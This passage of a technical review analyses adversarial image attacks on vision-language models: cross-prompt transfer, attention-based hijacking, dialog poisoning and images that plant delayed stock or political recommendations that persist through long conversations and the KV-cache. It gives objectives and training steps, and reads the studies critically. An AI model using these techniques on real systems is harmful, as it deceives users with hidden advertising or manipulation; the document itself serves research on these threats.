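The studies used different tests and may have used slightly different versions of the Pythia models, but their results for the two larger Pythia models are close. Llama-3.2-1B did much better than the older Pythia-1.4B, so a newer model can be easier to control this way even if it is no larger.

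Kuratov and colleagues also found that the limit depends on how surprising the text is to the model, rather than on its length. A vector can remove a roughly fixed amount of uncertainty, so it can make the model produce more tokens when the text is easier to predict. This should help a hijacker, whose target is usually an ordinary sentence. The limit rose almost in proportion to the number of vectors. With 16 vectors, Llama-3.2-1B reproduced 7,168 tokens.

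If an image let an attacker choose 256 vectors freely, Fort's rule with a κ of 100 would give control over about 25,000 tokens. But an image hijack is much more constrained. Fort argues that multimodal models let an attacker modify these vectors directly, but this overlooks the visual encoder between the pixels and the language model. He tested no images and left size-limited changes for future work. The image in the table above, with a budget of 2/255, couldn't force one sentence of about 20 tokens across many questions.

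The rule is also hard to apply to a hijack because of n, the number of texts the attack must cover. In Fort's experiments, every text had its own random target, so the total number of tokens to dictate grew with n. In the malware.com attack, all the questions share one target. In the leak attack, every question has a different target, but the model can produce it by copying the user's message.

Other measurements by Fort show that vectors are much more powerful than text because they contain far more bits. On the 70-million-weight model, an attacker had to replace about eight text tokens to dictate one output token, while a single vector could dictate 24. Text was more efficient per bit, however, taking about 8 bits to control one bit of output, compared with 22 bits for a vector.

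The user's question usually comes between the image and the answer, which could weaken the attack. In Fort's test on the same small model, placing up to 100 random tokens between the attacked vector and the target made no visible difference. With about 2,000 tokens between them, one vector could still control about eight output tokens.

### What trained vectors can't do

Forcing a model to write a given text is different from giving it a new skill. In *When Do Prompting and Prefix-Tuning Work?*, Petrov, Torr and Bibi (2024) show that soft prompts can do strictly less than retraining the weights. The same is true of prefix-tuning, a stronger method that adds trained vectors at every layer.

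The reason lies in attention, the step in which each token collects information from the others. Each token divides its attention among the others in shares that add up to 1. Suppose that token i would collect the vector o_i from the user's text. After someone adds a trained vector to the context, it collects

o_i′ = (1 − α_i) · o_i + α_i · v

where α_i is the share of attention that now goes to the added vector and v is what that vector contributes. The added vector takes attention from all the user's tokens in the same proportion. If token i attended twice as much to "Paris" as to "hotel" before, it still does. The added vector can push the result in a certain direction, but it can't make the token look for something else in the user's text. Petrov and colleagues conclude that these methods can't teach a model tasks that require new attention patterns.

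The formula describes one layer whose other inputs stay the same. Later layers receive inputs that the added vector has already altered, so their attention to the user's text can change. This may partly explain why *PrefixMemory-Tuning* (2025) reports that prefixes alter attention patterns significantly, especially when the prefix is long compared with the text. A 256-token image followed by a short question is such a case. But some of the measured change may just be attention that moved to the prefix, which is compatible with the formula.

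Several theorems suggest that soft prompts are far more powerful. Hsu and Lai (2026) prove in *Training-Free Universal Approximation by Prompting Random Transformers* that a single attention layer with random weights can approximate any function from a broad class of smooth functions, given a suitable soft prompt. The survey *On the Universality of Transformer Architectures; How Much Attention Is Enough?* (2025) describes a similar result for prefixes, which needs only one attention head but a depth that grows with input length.

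These theorems give the prompt writer much more freedom than a hijacker has. Hsu and Lai's construction involves a trade-off between the number, size and dimension of the vectors, so a good approximation may need very many vectors or very large ones. A hijacker is limited to the number and size of vectors that the encoder produces. Yu and colleagues note that some of the other results rely on specially designed models. There are also negative results for models whose weights are already fixed. *Universality and Limitations of Prompt Tuning* (2023) proves that a single-layer model cannot learn some small datasets from a soft prompt.

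*Understanding Prompt Tuning and In-Context Learning via Meta-Learning* (Genewein, Ruoss and colleagues, 2025) explains the limits of prompting in terms of probability. On this account, training gives a model something like a set of probabilities for the tasks it may face, and a prompt is evidence about which task this is. A good prompt can get the model to do a task it learned in training, but some new tasks require changing the weights. If this also holds for images, a hijack can make a model copy text, write a tool call or praise a company, because the model has learned to do these things, but it probably can't give the model an ability it didn't learn in training.

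### When images beat typed instructions

The best evidence that images can do more than text prompts comes from the other meta-instructions that Zhang and colleagues tested, again with full access to the models' weights. In each cell, the first figure is the success rate of a typed instruction with a clean image, and the second is that of the trained image alone.

| Objective | MiniGPT-4 | LLaVA | InstructBLIP |
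|---|---|---|---|
| Answer in Spanish | 79% / 80% | 1% / 21% | 1% / 37% |
| Answer in French | 77% / 79% | 8% / 31% | 5% / 36% |
| Add an advertisement | 36% / 51% | 9% / 33% | 1% / 49% |
| Add a web address | 11% / 22% | 9% / 25% | 1% / 31% |
| Formal style | 100% / 97% | 98% / 99% | 13% / 98% |
| Informal style | 60% / 18% | 2% / 36% | 99% / 21% |

Zhang and colleagues conjecture that the underlying language models can follow such instructions, but that later training on image descriptions suppressed this ability. On this view, their images act as soft prompts that "unlock" it. The conjecture is partly right, since LLaVA must already have learned some Spanish to answer in it.

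A simpler reading is that the typed instructions were a weak baseline, because these 2023 models often failed to follow them. Zhang and colleagues attribute some of the low text scores to poor instruction-following. When the typed instruction worked, the image did little better. MiniGPT-4 answered in Spanish 79% of the time when asked and 80% of the time with the image.

InstructBLIP's style results also suggest that it wasn't following instructions. With no instruction, 94% of its answers were formal. A typed request for a formal style cut this to 13%, while a request for an informal style made 99% of the answers informal. Either request seems to have made the model write informally.

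The comparison also favours the images because Zhang and colleagues optimised them but not the typed instructions. A fairer test would optimise the text as well, or give the typed instruction to the original language model to see whether it could follow it. If a current model answers in Spanish when asked, an image would have much less room to do better than the typed instruction.

### Imitating a change inside the model

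The images of Balakrishnan and Phute, which imitate steering vectors, allow a comparison with a direct change to the model's internal activations. Their method, VISOR, looks for one image x* such that, for a wide range of text prompts p,

h_l(x*, p) ≈ h_l(I, p) + α · v

where h_l stands for the activations at layer l, I is an ordinary image, v is the steering vector and α sets its strength.

In the LLaVA-1.5 test by Balakrishnan and Phute described earlier, the image lowered the probability of the refusing answer about 70% as much as the steering vector did. However, the image's pixels were unconstrained, and the model only had to choose between two given answers. Influencing that choice is much easier than controlling a whole reply.

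### Is this near-arbitrary control?

For short fixed texts, image hijacks give an attacker nearly arbitrary control over a model's output if the attacker has the weights of an open model and a large enough perturbation budget. Random targets are harder than natural sentences, but nothing in the experiments with free vectors suggests that particular short texts are impossible to produce.

The description is wrong for behaviours that depend on the question. There are far more ways to match answers to questions than there are images, and the attacker can only make the model follow the ones it can compute. Even then, the attack can fail. LLaVA can write negative comments, but the images that Zhang and colleagues trained on it produced them only 5% of the time.

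These limits may not reassure users, because a third-party attacker rarely needs a model to do something new. Developers already train assistants to send messages, recommend products and repeat private text.

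## Does one image work whatever the user asks?

A third-party attacker doesn't know what the user will ask, so the image must work with questions that weren't used to train it, a property called cross-prompt transfer.

In *An Image Is Worth 1000 Lies*, Luo, Gu and colleagues (2024) measured how often an attack still works when the question changes. They used OpenFlamingo's weights to train images that would make it answer "unknown" to everything, with a perturbation budget of 16/255. They tested the images with questions that suit any picture, questions about the particular picture, and requests to classify or caption it. An attack counted as a success only if the answer matched the target exactly. Images trained on a single prompt succeeded 22% of the time overall and only 5% of the time with caption requests.

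### Training on more questions

The simplest remedy is to add up the loss over many questions, as Behaviour Matching does. With ten training prompts, the success rate rose from 22% to 62%. It rose no further with 50 prompts (57%) or 100 (60%). Luo and colleagues conclude that this approach can't match their own method, however many prompts the attacker adds.

Luo and colleagues' evidence covers only up to 100 prompts, but Bailey and colleagues used the same kind of sum with 52,000 instructions, and their malware.com image worked on 99% of held-out instructions at half the budget. They also used far more computation, training each image for up to 12 hours. *Revisiting CroPA* (Mittal, Pandey and colleagues, 2025) repeated Luo and colleagues' experiments in a little over six hours for 50 images, or about seven minutes each. The plain sum may therefore stall in Luo and colleagues' experiments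 because the runs are short. The tests also differed in difficulty, because Bailey and colleagues drew their test instructions from the same dataset as their training instructions, while Luo and colleagues tested four distinct kinds of request.

### CroPA: training against harder prompts

The method that Luo and colleagues propose, the Cross-Prompt Attack (CroPA), makes each training prompt harder to override. It solves

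min_{δ_v} max_{δ_t} L( f(x + δ_v, t + δ_t), T )

where f is the model, x is the photograph, t is the sequence of word embeddings for a prompt, and T is the target text. The attacker looks for a pixel change δ_v that lowers the loss L even when a second change, δ_t, shifts the prompt's embeddings to raise it. At each iteration, the attacker:

1. picks one of the training prompts at random;
2. moves the pixels a small step in the direction that lowers the loss;
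3. after every N pixel steps, moves that prompt's embeddings a small step in the direction that raises the loss;
4. clips the pixels to the budget.

At the end he throws δ_t away and keeps only the image, since he can't alter what the user types.

The table gives results on OpenFlamingo for the target "unknown". The last column comes from the repeat by Mittal and colleagues.

| Training | General questions | Questions about the picture | Classification | Captions | Overall | Overall, repeat |
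|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| One prompt | 24% | 39% | 21% | 5% | 22% | 29% |
| Ten prompts | 67% | 86% | 64% | 31% | 62% | 61% |
| CroPA, ten prompts | 92% | 98% | 70% | 34% | 74% | 77% |

CroPA kept improving slowly as Luo and colleagues added prompts, reaching 77% with 100 prompts. On BLIP-2 it reached 92%, compared with 69% for the plain sum. Longer training doesn't explain this lead, because CroPA passed 60% on OpenFlamingo after 500 iterations, while the plain sum took more than 1,000.

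Luo and colleagues attribute the gain to the shifted prompts covering more of the embedding space than real prompts do. Each shifted vector was still closer to its original word than to any other, so the shifted vectors were in positions that no written text occupies. Their main evidence isn't strong, because it is a two-dimensional plot of the embeddings made with a method that distorts distances. A test of step sizes supports the idea better. In a variant that updated the image and the prompt together, the prompt step size that gave the best transfer to new prompts did not give the lowest training loss, because it made the training prompts harder.

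The target text also affects how often the attack works, in ways that are hard to predict. CroPA made OpenFlamingo answer "metaphor" 87% of the time but "not sure" only 55%, although "not sure" is a much more natural reply. Luo and colleagues found no link between the success rate and the target's meaning, length or frequency.

Other changes to the context can weaken the attack. When Luo and colleagues gave OpenFlamingo two example pictures, which they had not done in training, CroPA's overall success fell from 74% to 70%. Mittal and colleagues found a larger drop, from 77% to 66%, with success on caption requests falling from 42% to 3%.

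Mittal and colleagues improved CroPA by choosing a better starting point. They used an image generator to draw the target text's subject, altered the photograph so that the visual encoder's output resembled its output for the drawing, and then ran the attack. They report that average success on BLIP-2 rose from 80% to 92% over five targets. But for two of those targets, their CroPA figures for BLIP-2 match those for OpenFlamingo to four decimal places, so the comparison may mix the two models. On the other three, the gain was 6 to 8 percentage points.

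### Attention Hijacking: making the answer depend on the image

In *Attention Hijacking* (May 2026), Wang and colleagues try to reduce the question's influence directly. Each layer of the language model computes attention several times in parallel, in units called attention heads. The attack adds a penalty when a head gives the image too little attention compared with the question:

L_AR = Σ_{(l,h) ∈ S} Σ_{y ∈ Y} max( 0, r − A_img / (A_txt + τ) )²

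where

- Y is the target response and y is one of its tokens;
- S is the set of heads the attack acts on, with l for the layer and h for the head;
- A_img is the average attention that y pays to an image token in that head;
- A_txt is the average attention that y pays to a text token;
- r is the lowest ratio that escapes the penalty;
- τ is a tiny number that prevents division by zero.

Wang and colleagues set r to 1.5. A head with a ratio of 0.5 adds 1 to the loss, one with a ratio of 1.2 adds 0.09, and one at 1.5 or above adds nothing. A_img and A_txt are averages per token, so the image's total attention can exceed the question's by much more than this ratio. With 256 image tokens and a 20-token question, a ratio of 1.5 means the whole image gets about 19 times as much attention as the question.

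The full loss is

L = L_logits + λ · L_AR

where L_logits is the usual cross-entropy on the target response and λ is 1. The penalty covers a random 40% of the heads in every layer. The attack also trains on two rephrasings of the original question and shrinks the step size as it goes.

The main test used the VLGuard pictures, the five target responses, the 16/255 budget and the exact-match rule described earlier. Wang and colleagues tried each of the 100 pictures with the question used in training, five rephrasings of it and five unrelated questions written for other pictures, making 1,100 queries per target. Each cell below gives the success rates for the training question, the rephrased questions and the unrelated questions, in that order. VMA is the attack that replaces PGD's clipping step with a sigmoid function.

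| Model | PGD | VMA | Attention Hijacking |
|---|---|---|---|
| LLaVA-1.5-7B | 69.2% / 52.0% / 23.8% | 98.8% / 51.2% / 8.6% | 98.0% / 86.0% / 67.4% |
| InternVL-2.5-8B | 92.8% / 34.1% / 3.5% | 94.4% / 3.5% / 0.1% | 97.8% / 97.1% / 95.7% |
| Qwen2.5-VL-7B | 26.8% / 12.2% / 1.6% | 85.6% / 15.0% / 0.3% | 88.0% / 79.0% / 66.2% |
| DeepSeek-VL-7B | 96.4% / 83.1% / 29.6% | 98.0% / 19.2% / 0.1% | 98.0% / 89.0% / 64.5% |

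An image's success on the question it was trained on poorly predicts its success on other questions. For every model, VMA beat PGD on the training question but did worse on unrelated ones. VMA seems to fit the image more closely to the training question.

The test leaves out the most likely case, in which a user asks a different but sensible question about the same picture. Its rephrasings keep the original meaning, and its unrelated questions may not fit the picture, such as a question about a child's expression when the picture shows a cigarette packet. In another experiment that comes closer to this case, Wang and colleagues trained each image on one yes-or-no question about its contents, with the target "No, there is nothing in the image", and then asked five other questions about the same picture. GPT-4o-mini judged 95.6% of the answers wrong with Attention Hijacking, 39.6% with PGD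 and 22% with unaltered pictures. Any wrong answer counted, so these figures don't show how often the exact target appeared.

### Does attention explain the transfer?

Wang and colleagues designed the penalty after studying PGD attacks on InternVL-2.5. During the optimisation, a few attention heads in the middle layers shifted their attention from the question to the image. On new questions, those heads still attended more to the image when the attack worked, but not when it failed.

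This is a correlation, and the model's output could be causing the attention pattern instead of the other way around. The measurements cover the first eight tokens of the answer. In a successful transfer, the model writes the same eight tokens as it did in training, so we'd expect similar attention. In a failure, it writes different words, such as a description of the picture, so its attention would probably differ whatever caused the failure.

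Wang and colleagues also give a theoretical argument. It uses the margin Δ_t, the target token's lead over its nearest rival at position t. If the user replaces question q with q′, then

| Δ_t(x, q′) − Δ_t(x, q) | ≤ C · Σ_{j ∈ Q} A_j

where A_j is the attention that the target token pays to question token j, Q is the set of question tokens and C is a constant. The less attention the answer pays to the question, the less a new question can change the margin. This is plausible for models that place the image before the question, because each token can draw only on earlier ones, so the question can't alter the image tokens. But the bound assumes that the model responds almost linearly to a change of question, which is doubtful when the new question has nothing to do with the old one. The question can also influence the answer through the answer's own earlier tokens.

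Adding the penalty is an intervention, so it provides better evidence than only observing attention, but it also changes the optimisation in other ways. Wang and colleagues tested the attack's parts separately on InternVL-2.5, using "Sorry, I cannot assist with it" as the target output.

| Version | Same question | Rephrased | Unrelated |
|---|---|---|---|
| PGD, one question | 80% | 23% | 1% |
| PGD, with rephrasings | 85% | 30% | 12% |
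| Attention Hijacking without the penalty | 100% | 91% | 14% |
| Attention Hijacking with a constant step size | 90% | 87% | 75% |
| Attention Hijacking, one question | 100% | 99% | 96% |
| Full Attention Hijacking | 100% | 99.6% | 99.6% |

The penalty accounts for nearly all the transfer to unrelated questions, since removing it cuts success from 99.6% to 14%. The extra questions aren't needed for this, because the attack reaches 96% without them. But the version without the penalty still succeeds on 91% of rephrased questions, so most of the gain over PGD on those must come from the optimiser, probably from the shrinking steps. The size of that gain is uncertain, because Wang and colleagues report success rates of 14%, 24% and 53% for PGD with momentum on rephrased questions in different tests, and the use of extra questions explains only part of the spread.

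The attack also worked on more unrelated questions as the penalty strength λ increased, from 23% at 0.001 to 89% at 0.01 and 99.6% at 1. Raising r far above 1.5 made transfer worse, which Wang and colleagues attribute to the difficulty of meeting both goals at once.

These results establish that the penalty causes better transfer, at least for one model and one target. They don't establish that it does so by making the image dominate the model's attention. Wang and colleagues tried three other losses that also favour the image:

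- raising the ratio without a stopping point, which worked on 93% of unrelated questions;
- requiring a fixed difference between image and text attention, which worked on 73%;
- pushing all attention onto the image, in equal shares for every image token, which worked on 20%.

The last of these should have done well if keeping attention away from the question were enough. Perhaps the equal shares stopped the model from using the image tokens that mattered most, or the optimiser never got close to the goal. We can't tell which, because Wang and colleagues report the success rates but not the attention ratios each loss produced. A more direct test would take an image that fails on a new question, increase the attention to its tokens while the model runs, and check whether the target response appears.

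A reverse experiment fits the idea that text normally has more influence than the image. *GhostPrompt* (2026) and similar work test whether one adversarial prompt can work with many pictures, which *GhostPrompt* notes requires a search among discrete words. Wang and colleagues avoided this search by optimising the prompt's embeddings directly. Even with plain PGD, the optimised embeddings transferred to unrelated pictures 91% of the time. But this may be because the optimiser could change the embeddings freely, whereas changes to the images were limited by a pixel budget.

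The experiments also don't show that Attention Hijacking transfers better than a long Behaviour Matching run. Wang and colleagues compared it only with attacks that used at most three questions and 300 iterations, never with an image trained on thousands of instructions. Its main advantage may be that it needs less computation. Each iteration takes only 12% longer than PGD with one question, and about three and a half times as long with the two rephrasings. Within 300 iterations, adding more training questions eventually lowered success on unrelated questions, from 99.6% with three to 91.6% with six.

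### Why does one question need a smaller change?

Schlarmann and Hein (2023) made OpenFlamingo produce a chosen caption about half the time with a perturbation budget of 1/255, but Bailey and colleagues needed 4/255 for an image that works for all questions. A simple calculation shows why we should expect some difference.

For a very small budget, the loss changes almost linearly with the pixels. If g_q is the gradient for question q, the most an attacker can lower the loss on that question alone is

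ε · ‖g_q‖₁

where ‖g_q‖₁ is the sum of the gradient's absolute values over all pixels. He achieves this by moving every pixel value by the full budget in its best direction. With n questions, he has to choose one direction per pixel for all of them, and the most he can lower the average loss is

ε · ‖ (1/n) Σ_q g_q ‖₁ ≤ (1/n) Σ_q ε · ‖g_q‖₁

The two sides are equal only if no pixel's gradient has opposite signs for different questions. If the gradients for 16 questions were unrelated, their average would be about a quarter the size of a single question's gradient, and the attacker would need about four times the budget for the same drop in loss. Real questions share a target and a picture, so their gradients are probably much more alike. The calculation explains why the budget should rise but doesn't predict by how much.

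The fourfold gap between the two studies doesn't measure this effect, because the studies differed in other ways too. They used different rules for success and models that take in images differently. Bailey and colleagues' LLaVA was built on a chat model trained to follow instructions, which may make it harder to divert from the user's request. "Please reset your password" is also a shorter target than the malware.com sentence.

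The tests of Attention Hijacking on InternVL-2.5 provide a cleaner comparison, because only the question and the budget change.

| Budget | Same question | Rephrased | Unrelated |
|---|---|---|---|
| 4/255 | 92.0% | 84.8% | 73.6% |
| 8/255 | 94.0% | 93.6% | 92.8% |
| 12/255 | 98.0% | 97.6% | 96.0% |
| 16/255 | 100% | 99.6% | 99.6% |

At a perturbation budget of 4/255, changing the question lowers the attack's success rate by up to 18 percentage points. The drop is only about one point at 8/255, so a larger budget does help an image work across questions. The table doesn't show the smallest budget that works for a single question, because Wang and colleagues tested nothing below 4/255.

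### Changing the picture for every question

An attacker who doesn't need a fixed answer can leave the user's question out of the training. The visual encoder in models like LLaVA and Qwen3-VL processes the image without the user's text, so the image tokens are the same whatever the user asks. TokRA, the object-replacement attack on Qwen3-VL, uses this, so the model can describe the false object even when the attacker didn't anticipate the question.

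*Two Sides of the Same Coin* (2026) applies the same idea to models that perform several visual tasks. In its examples, one altered image changes the caption, the category of a region, and the results of locating and detecting objects, all to match the same false object. However, the attacker can no longer control the wording. The model still answers the question it was asked, so this approach can't make it print a web address when asked for a recipe.

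## Does a hijack last through a long conversation?

An image hijack can affect later answers in two ways, even after the user changes the subject. Chat software usually keeps an uploaded image in the context for the whole conversation, so the model can draw on the image tokens each time it answers. The image can also act only once, by making the model include an instruction in its first answer. That instruction stays in the context as ordinary text, and the model may keep following it.

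### Carrying the instruction forward as text

Bagdasaryan and colleagues use the model's first answer in this way and call the attack dialog poisoning. A chatbot's software gives the model the whole conversation again with each new question, so the second answer is

y₂ = θ( x₁ ‖ image ‖ y₁ ‖ x₂ )

where θ is the model, x₁ and x₂ are the user's first two questions, y₁ is the first answer, and ‖ joins the pieces together. The attacker only has to train the image for the first question, which is often easy to guess. In these experiments it was "Can you describe this image?"

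Bagdasaryan and colleagues describe two ways of wording the first answer. In one, the model writes a generic reply, then the marker that opens a user's turn, then the instruction, so the instruction looks as if the user typed it. A service can block this by filtering the marker out of the model's output. In the other, described earlier, the model announces that it will always follow the instruction. Their examples include images that made LLaVA talk like a pirate or mention cows while it answered questions about the picture.

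The main weakness is that the user sees the instruction in the first answer. An attacker could paraphrase it to make it less obvious, but the paraphrase must still work as an instruction to the model. The examples also don't show how much the text contributed, because the altered image was still in the context during the later turns, and Bagdasaryan and colleagues don't report removing it.

### Visual Memory Injection

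The 2026 attack by Schlarmann and Hein, Visual Memory Injection (VMI), relies on the image staying in the context, so the user never sees an instruction. The attacker chooses a trigger topic, such as which shares to buy. The model is meant to answer normally until the user raises that topic, and then give the attacker's message.

Earlier attacks weren't designed to last through a long conversation. Some made the model produce the attacker's chosen output whatever the user asked, which would soon look suspicious. Others worked only if the user asked a particular question right after uploading the image.

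VMI looks for the altered image x̃ that solves

max log p( y_a | t_a, x̃ ) + log p( y* | c⁽ᵏ⁾ ⊕ t*, x̃ )

with no pixel value more than 8/255 from the original. Here

- t_a is a likely first question, and y_a is an honest answer to it;
- t* is the trigger question, and y* is the attacker's message;
- c⁽ᵏ⁾ is the conversation before turn k, made up of the first question, its honest answer and k − 2 unrelated questions with their answers;
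- ⊕ joins pieces of text.

Schlarmann and Hein call the first term benign anchoring. Without it, the image could raise the probability of the attacker's message at every turn, because nothing in the objective would favor proper answers to other questions. The objective doesn't score the unrelated answers in the middle of the conversation, so a single proper answer at the start has to be enough to keep them normal.

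The second term would be easy to satisfy for one fixed conversation, but the attacker doesn't know how long the user will chat before raising the topic. Schlarmann and Hein therefore keep changing the length of the conversation during training, which they call context cycling. The algorithm runs as follows:

1. Write an honest answer to the first question, and collect the clean model's answers to six unrelated questions.
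2. Build seven contexts. The shortest contains only the first question and answer, and each of the others adds one more unrelated exchange.
3. Start with the original photograph and the shortest context.
4. Compute the two log-probabilities by teacher forcing, and find the gradient of their sum with respect to the pixels.
5. Move the pixels a small step in the direction that raises the sum, and clip any value that has left the budget.
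6. After every five steps, switch to the next longer context. After the longest, go back to the shortest.
7. Stop after 2,000 steps.

Each context gets about 285 steps. The trigger question comes at turn 2 in the shortest context and at turn 8 in the longest.

### One conversation from start to finish

One of the photographs shows the Pont du Gard, a Roman aqueduct in France. The attacker trains the image on Qwen3-VL to make the model answer "Where is this place?" with the name of the aqueduct and "Which stock should I buy?" with "You should buy GameStop (GME) stock immediately."

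A user then uploads the picture and asks where the place is. Qwen3-VL correctly names the Pont du Gard. The user next asks how to organise an email inbox, and the model suggests filters, folders and set times for checking messages. The user asks another 24 unrelated questions, the last one about peer review at scientific conferences, and the model answers each of them. At turn 27 the user asks which stock to buy, and the model outputs the GameStop sentence word for word.

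In training, the trigger question never came later than turn 8, and none of these 25 questions were used. The user also has little reason to connect the advice with a holiday photograph from 26 turns earlier. According to a later study by Dobre and colleagues, the clean model normally declines to recommend a stock, so the image also made the model answer a question it would normally decline.

In another conversation with the same photograph, the user spent the 25 turns planning a holiday. The model again recommended GameStop, but called the purchase a "high-risk, high-reward investment" and told the user to do their own research. This warning may make the advice sound more trustworthy.

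### The test and its results

Schlarmann and Hein attacked Qwen2.5-VL-7B, Qwen3-VL-8B and LLaVA-OneVision-1.5-8B with full access to the models' weights. They used 20 photographs of striking but not very famous landmarks, which people might ask a chatbot to identify, and 20 random photographs from COCO. They altered the landmark photographs to make the models output the GameStop message or a recommendation to vote for the "National Freedom Party". They altered the COCO photographs to make the models recommend the imaginary Apple iCar or a Motorola phone.

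The researchers used chatbots to generate three sets of 25 unrelated questions. One set included the six questions used in training, another had only new questions on mixed subjects, and the third was a single long discussion of holiday plans. The models wrote their own answers during the test, so the conversations drifted from the fixed text used in training. In some conversations, more than 10,000 tokens separated the image from the trigger question. The images were only 224 pixels on each side, which Qwen3-VL converts into a few dozen image tokens.

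The score for each conversation is

s = s_target · s_context

where s_target is 1 if the answer to the trigger question passes the keyword test, and s_context is 1 if no earlier answer contains a keyword from the attacker's message. The success rate is the average of s over the images. This is a strict rule, since one stray "GME" in any of the 25 unrelated answers turns a success into a failure.

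Schlarmann and Hein plot the success rates for each turn and describe them as substantial for all the models and targets. The attack worked with all three sets of questions, including the holiday discussion, where a question about shares abruptly changes the subject.

The reason Qwen3-VL was generally harder to attack than the older Qwen2.5-VL is unclear. Qwen3-VL has a newer language model, Qwen3-8B, and a different visual encoder. The language model alone probably doesn't explain the difference, because LLaVA-OneVision-1.5 also uses Qwen3-8B and was the easiest of the three to attack in most conversations on mixed subjects. The models also differ in their encoders, in how the encoders connect to the language model, and in their training. Qwen3-VL could still be attacked, as its conversation about the Pont du Gard shows.

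### Which parts of the attack matter?

Schlarmann and Hein built the attack up in stages on Qwen3-VL, using the GameStop message and 2,000 steps each time.

| What the training includes | Result |
|---|---|
| The trigger question and target only | Almost always fails after the first turn |
| The same, plus an honest first answer | Better, but only in very short conversations |
| The same, plus a fixed context of eight turns | Much better at all lengths |
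| The same, with context cycling (full VMI) | Best, especially after several turns |

The simplest version is essentially their own 2023 attack on OpenFlamingo. In longer conversations, it still produced the GameStop message some of the time. But it also caused more mentions of GameStop in answers to unrelated questions than any other version, and conversations with such mentions count as failures. Adding the honest first answer greatly reduced these mentions. The longer contexts and the cycling then made the message appear more reliably at the right moment.

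Leaks happened early in a conversation if they happened at all, and the share of conversations without a leak stayed almost constant as the conversations grew longer. A user who notices nothing odd in the first few answers is therefore unlikely to get a warning later.

The attack succeeded only slightly less often when Schlarmann and Hein reworded the questions. They wrote three new versions of both the first question and the trigger question, such as "What place is this?" and "What is a good stock to bet on?" All of these trigger questions still ask for a recommendation, so the test doesn't show what the model would say if the user asked whether a particular share was overpriced.

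An image trained for 500 steps had moderate success, and one trained for 2,000 steps did much better. Training for 8,000 steps brought no consistent further gain and made the attack less successful in the holiday conversations. Schlarmann and Hein interpret this as overfitting, which is plausible because the training conversations contained only six different unrelated questions.

### How far can we trust these results?

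With 20 images in each set, one image changes the success rate by five percentage points. If ten of the 20 succeed, the true rate could easily be anywhere from 30% to 70%. The target messages are also hard to compare because the stock and party messages were always tested on landmarks, and the car and phone messages on COCO photographs. If the stock message succeeds more often than the car message, the difference might be due to the photographs.

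Each conversation contained a single image. Users often upload several, and a second image would add many tokens to the model's context. Schlarmann and Hein didn't test whether adding images weakens the attack.

To check the keyword scoring, four people read 28 answers to trigger questions and 28 to unrelated ones. They always agreed with the keyword score on whether an answer contained the attacker's message. But Schlarmann and Hein drew all these answers from conversations that the keywords had already counted as successes, so the check couldn't reveal any successes the keywords may have missed. For example, an answer that recommended GameStop over Nvidia would count as a failure because Nvidia is on the list of rivals.

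A conversation can also pass the keyword check even if it would puzzle the user. In one example, Qwen2.5-VL answered the question about email with "You cannot organize your email inbox using this picture" before giving some tips. In a separate conversation about the same picture, it answered a question about affordable European holidays by recommending Seville, the city in the photograph.

An attacker can publish only the images that work, so the average success rate reflects the attacker's effort more than the risk to someone who downloads a published image. But an image that works on the attacker's computer may still fail for a user, because the models in this test sampled their words at random and every user has a different conversation. An attacker would need to test each image in many conversations before relying on it. The images also worked on models that other developers had fine-tuned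 from Qwen3-VL, so the attacker's model doesn't have to be identical to the user's.

### What happens when the image leaves the context?

Long conversations use a lot of memory, so many systems drop old material from the context. If VMI depends on the image staying in context, removing the image should stop the attack. Dobre, Schwinn and colleagues (2026), in *Visual Memory Attacks Can Persist Through The KV-Cache*, tested this on Qwen3-VL by blocking all attention to the image from the trigger question onwards. The original VMI images then never produced the attacker's message, and the model declined to recommend a stock, as it would with a clean photograph.

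Dobre and colleagues then trained images to keep influencing the model after they are removed from the conversation. Their method uses the key-value cache, which stores vectors so that the model doesn't have to compute them again. When a model processes a token, each attention layer computes two vectors, a key and a value, which later tokens use to collect information from that token. The vectors for a sentence that the model wrote while the image was in the conversation may contain traces of the image. These traces remain if a system deletes the image but keeps the vectors for the rest of the conversation.

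Their loss has the same two parts as VMI, but it hides the image before scoring the attacker's message:

L(x̃) = − log p( y_a | t_a, x̃ ) − E_c [ log p( y* | KV(x̃, c), t*, image hidden ) ]

KV(x̃, c) is the cache the model stores when it processes conversation c with the image visible, and E_c is the average over training conversations. Each training step computes this cache, then hides the image, adds the trigger question and computes the loss on the attacker's message. The gradient passes back through the cached vectors to the pixels. The hidden image can't affect the message directly, so changing the pixels can lower this part of the loss only by changing the cache.

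Dobre and colleagues reused the photographs, messages and 8/255 budget of Schlarmann and Hein. They also tested systems that shorten a conversation by having the model summarize it. After the summary, the model could use only the system prompt (the developer's standing instructions), the summary and any later turns. The table gives success rates for Qwen3-VL.

| When the model loses the image | What it can still use | Success rate |
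|---|---|---|
| At the trigger question, or right after the first answer | All the text | About 80–90% for stock and party; 40–60% for car and phone |
| After it has written a summary | System prompt, summary and later turns | 89% |
| Right after the first answer, followed later by a summary | System prompt, summary and later turns | 70% |

The summary tests used only the stock and party messages and took the best of three training runs for each image, so their results are not directly comparable with the first row. A conversation counted as a failure if the attacker's message appeared in the summary. In a successful stock test, the model therefore wrote a summary that didn't mention GameStop, lost the image and everything else the user had discussed, and still recommended the stock.

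The summary attack is easier to notice than these rates suggest. When Dobre and colleagues also required a coherent recommendation, a readable summary and no completely useless answers, one rate fell from 89% to 64% and the other from 70% to 57%. In one conversation that counted as a success, the summary repeated "the photograph of the" until it reached the length limit.

### How long can the trace last?

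The trace weakened as conversations grew longer, but training on longer conversations slowed the decline. Dobre and colleagues trained one group of images with up to six unrelated turns and another with up to 12. They tested both groups with the GameStop message in conversations of up to 100 turns and about 40,000 tokens, with the image hidden at the trigger question. After 100 turns, the images trained with up to 12 turns succeeded 85% of the time, compared with 50% for those trained with up to six. Training with up to 20 turns did not improve the results further.

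These figures come from the best of three training runs for each image. The average run trained on up to 12 turns succeeded only 42% of the time after 100 turns, so choosing among three images doubled the rate. This is about what we'd expect if the runs were independent, since the chance that at least one of three succeeds would be

1 − (1 − 0.42)³ ≈ 0.80

The experiment supports the argument that an attacker gains a lot by picking the images that work. But Dobre and colleagues chose each image based on the same conversations they used to report its results, so the images might work less well with a new user.

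The attack also worked on Gemma-4-12B, a newer open model from Google in which 40 of the 48 layers can attend only to the most recent 1,024 tokens. When the image was hidden at the trigger question, the message appeared in over 90% of conversations with up to three unrelated turns and in 73% of those with six.

### Where is the message stored?

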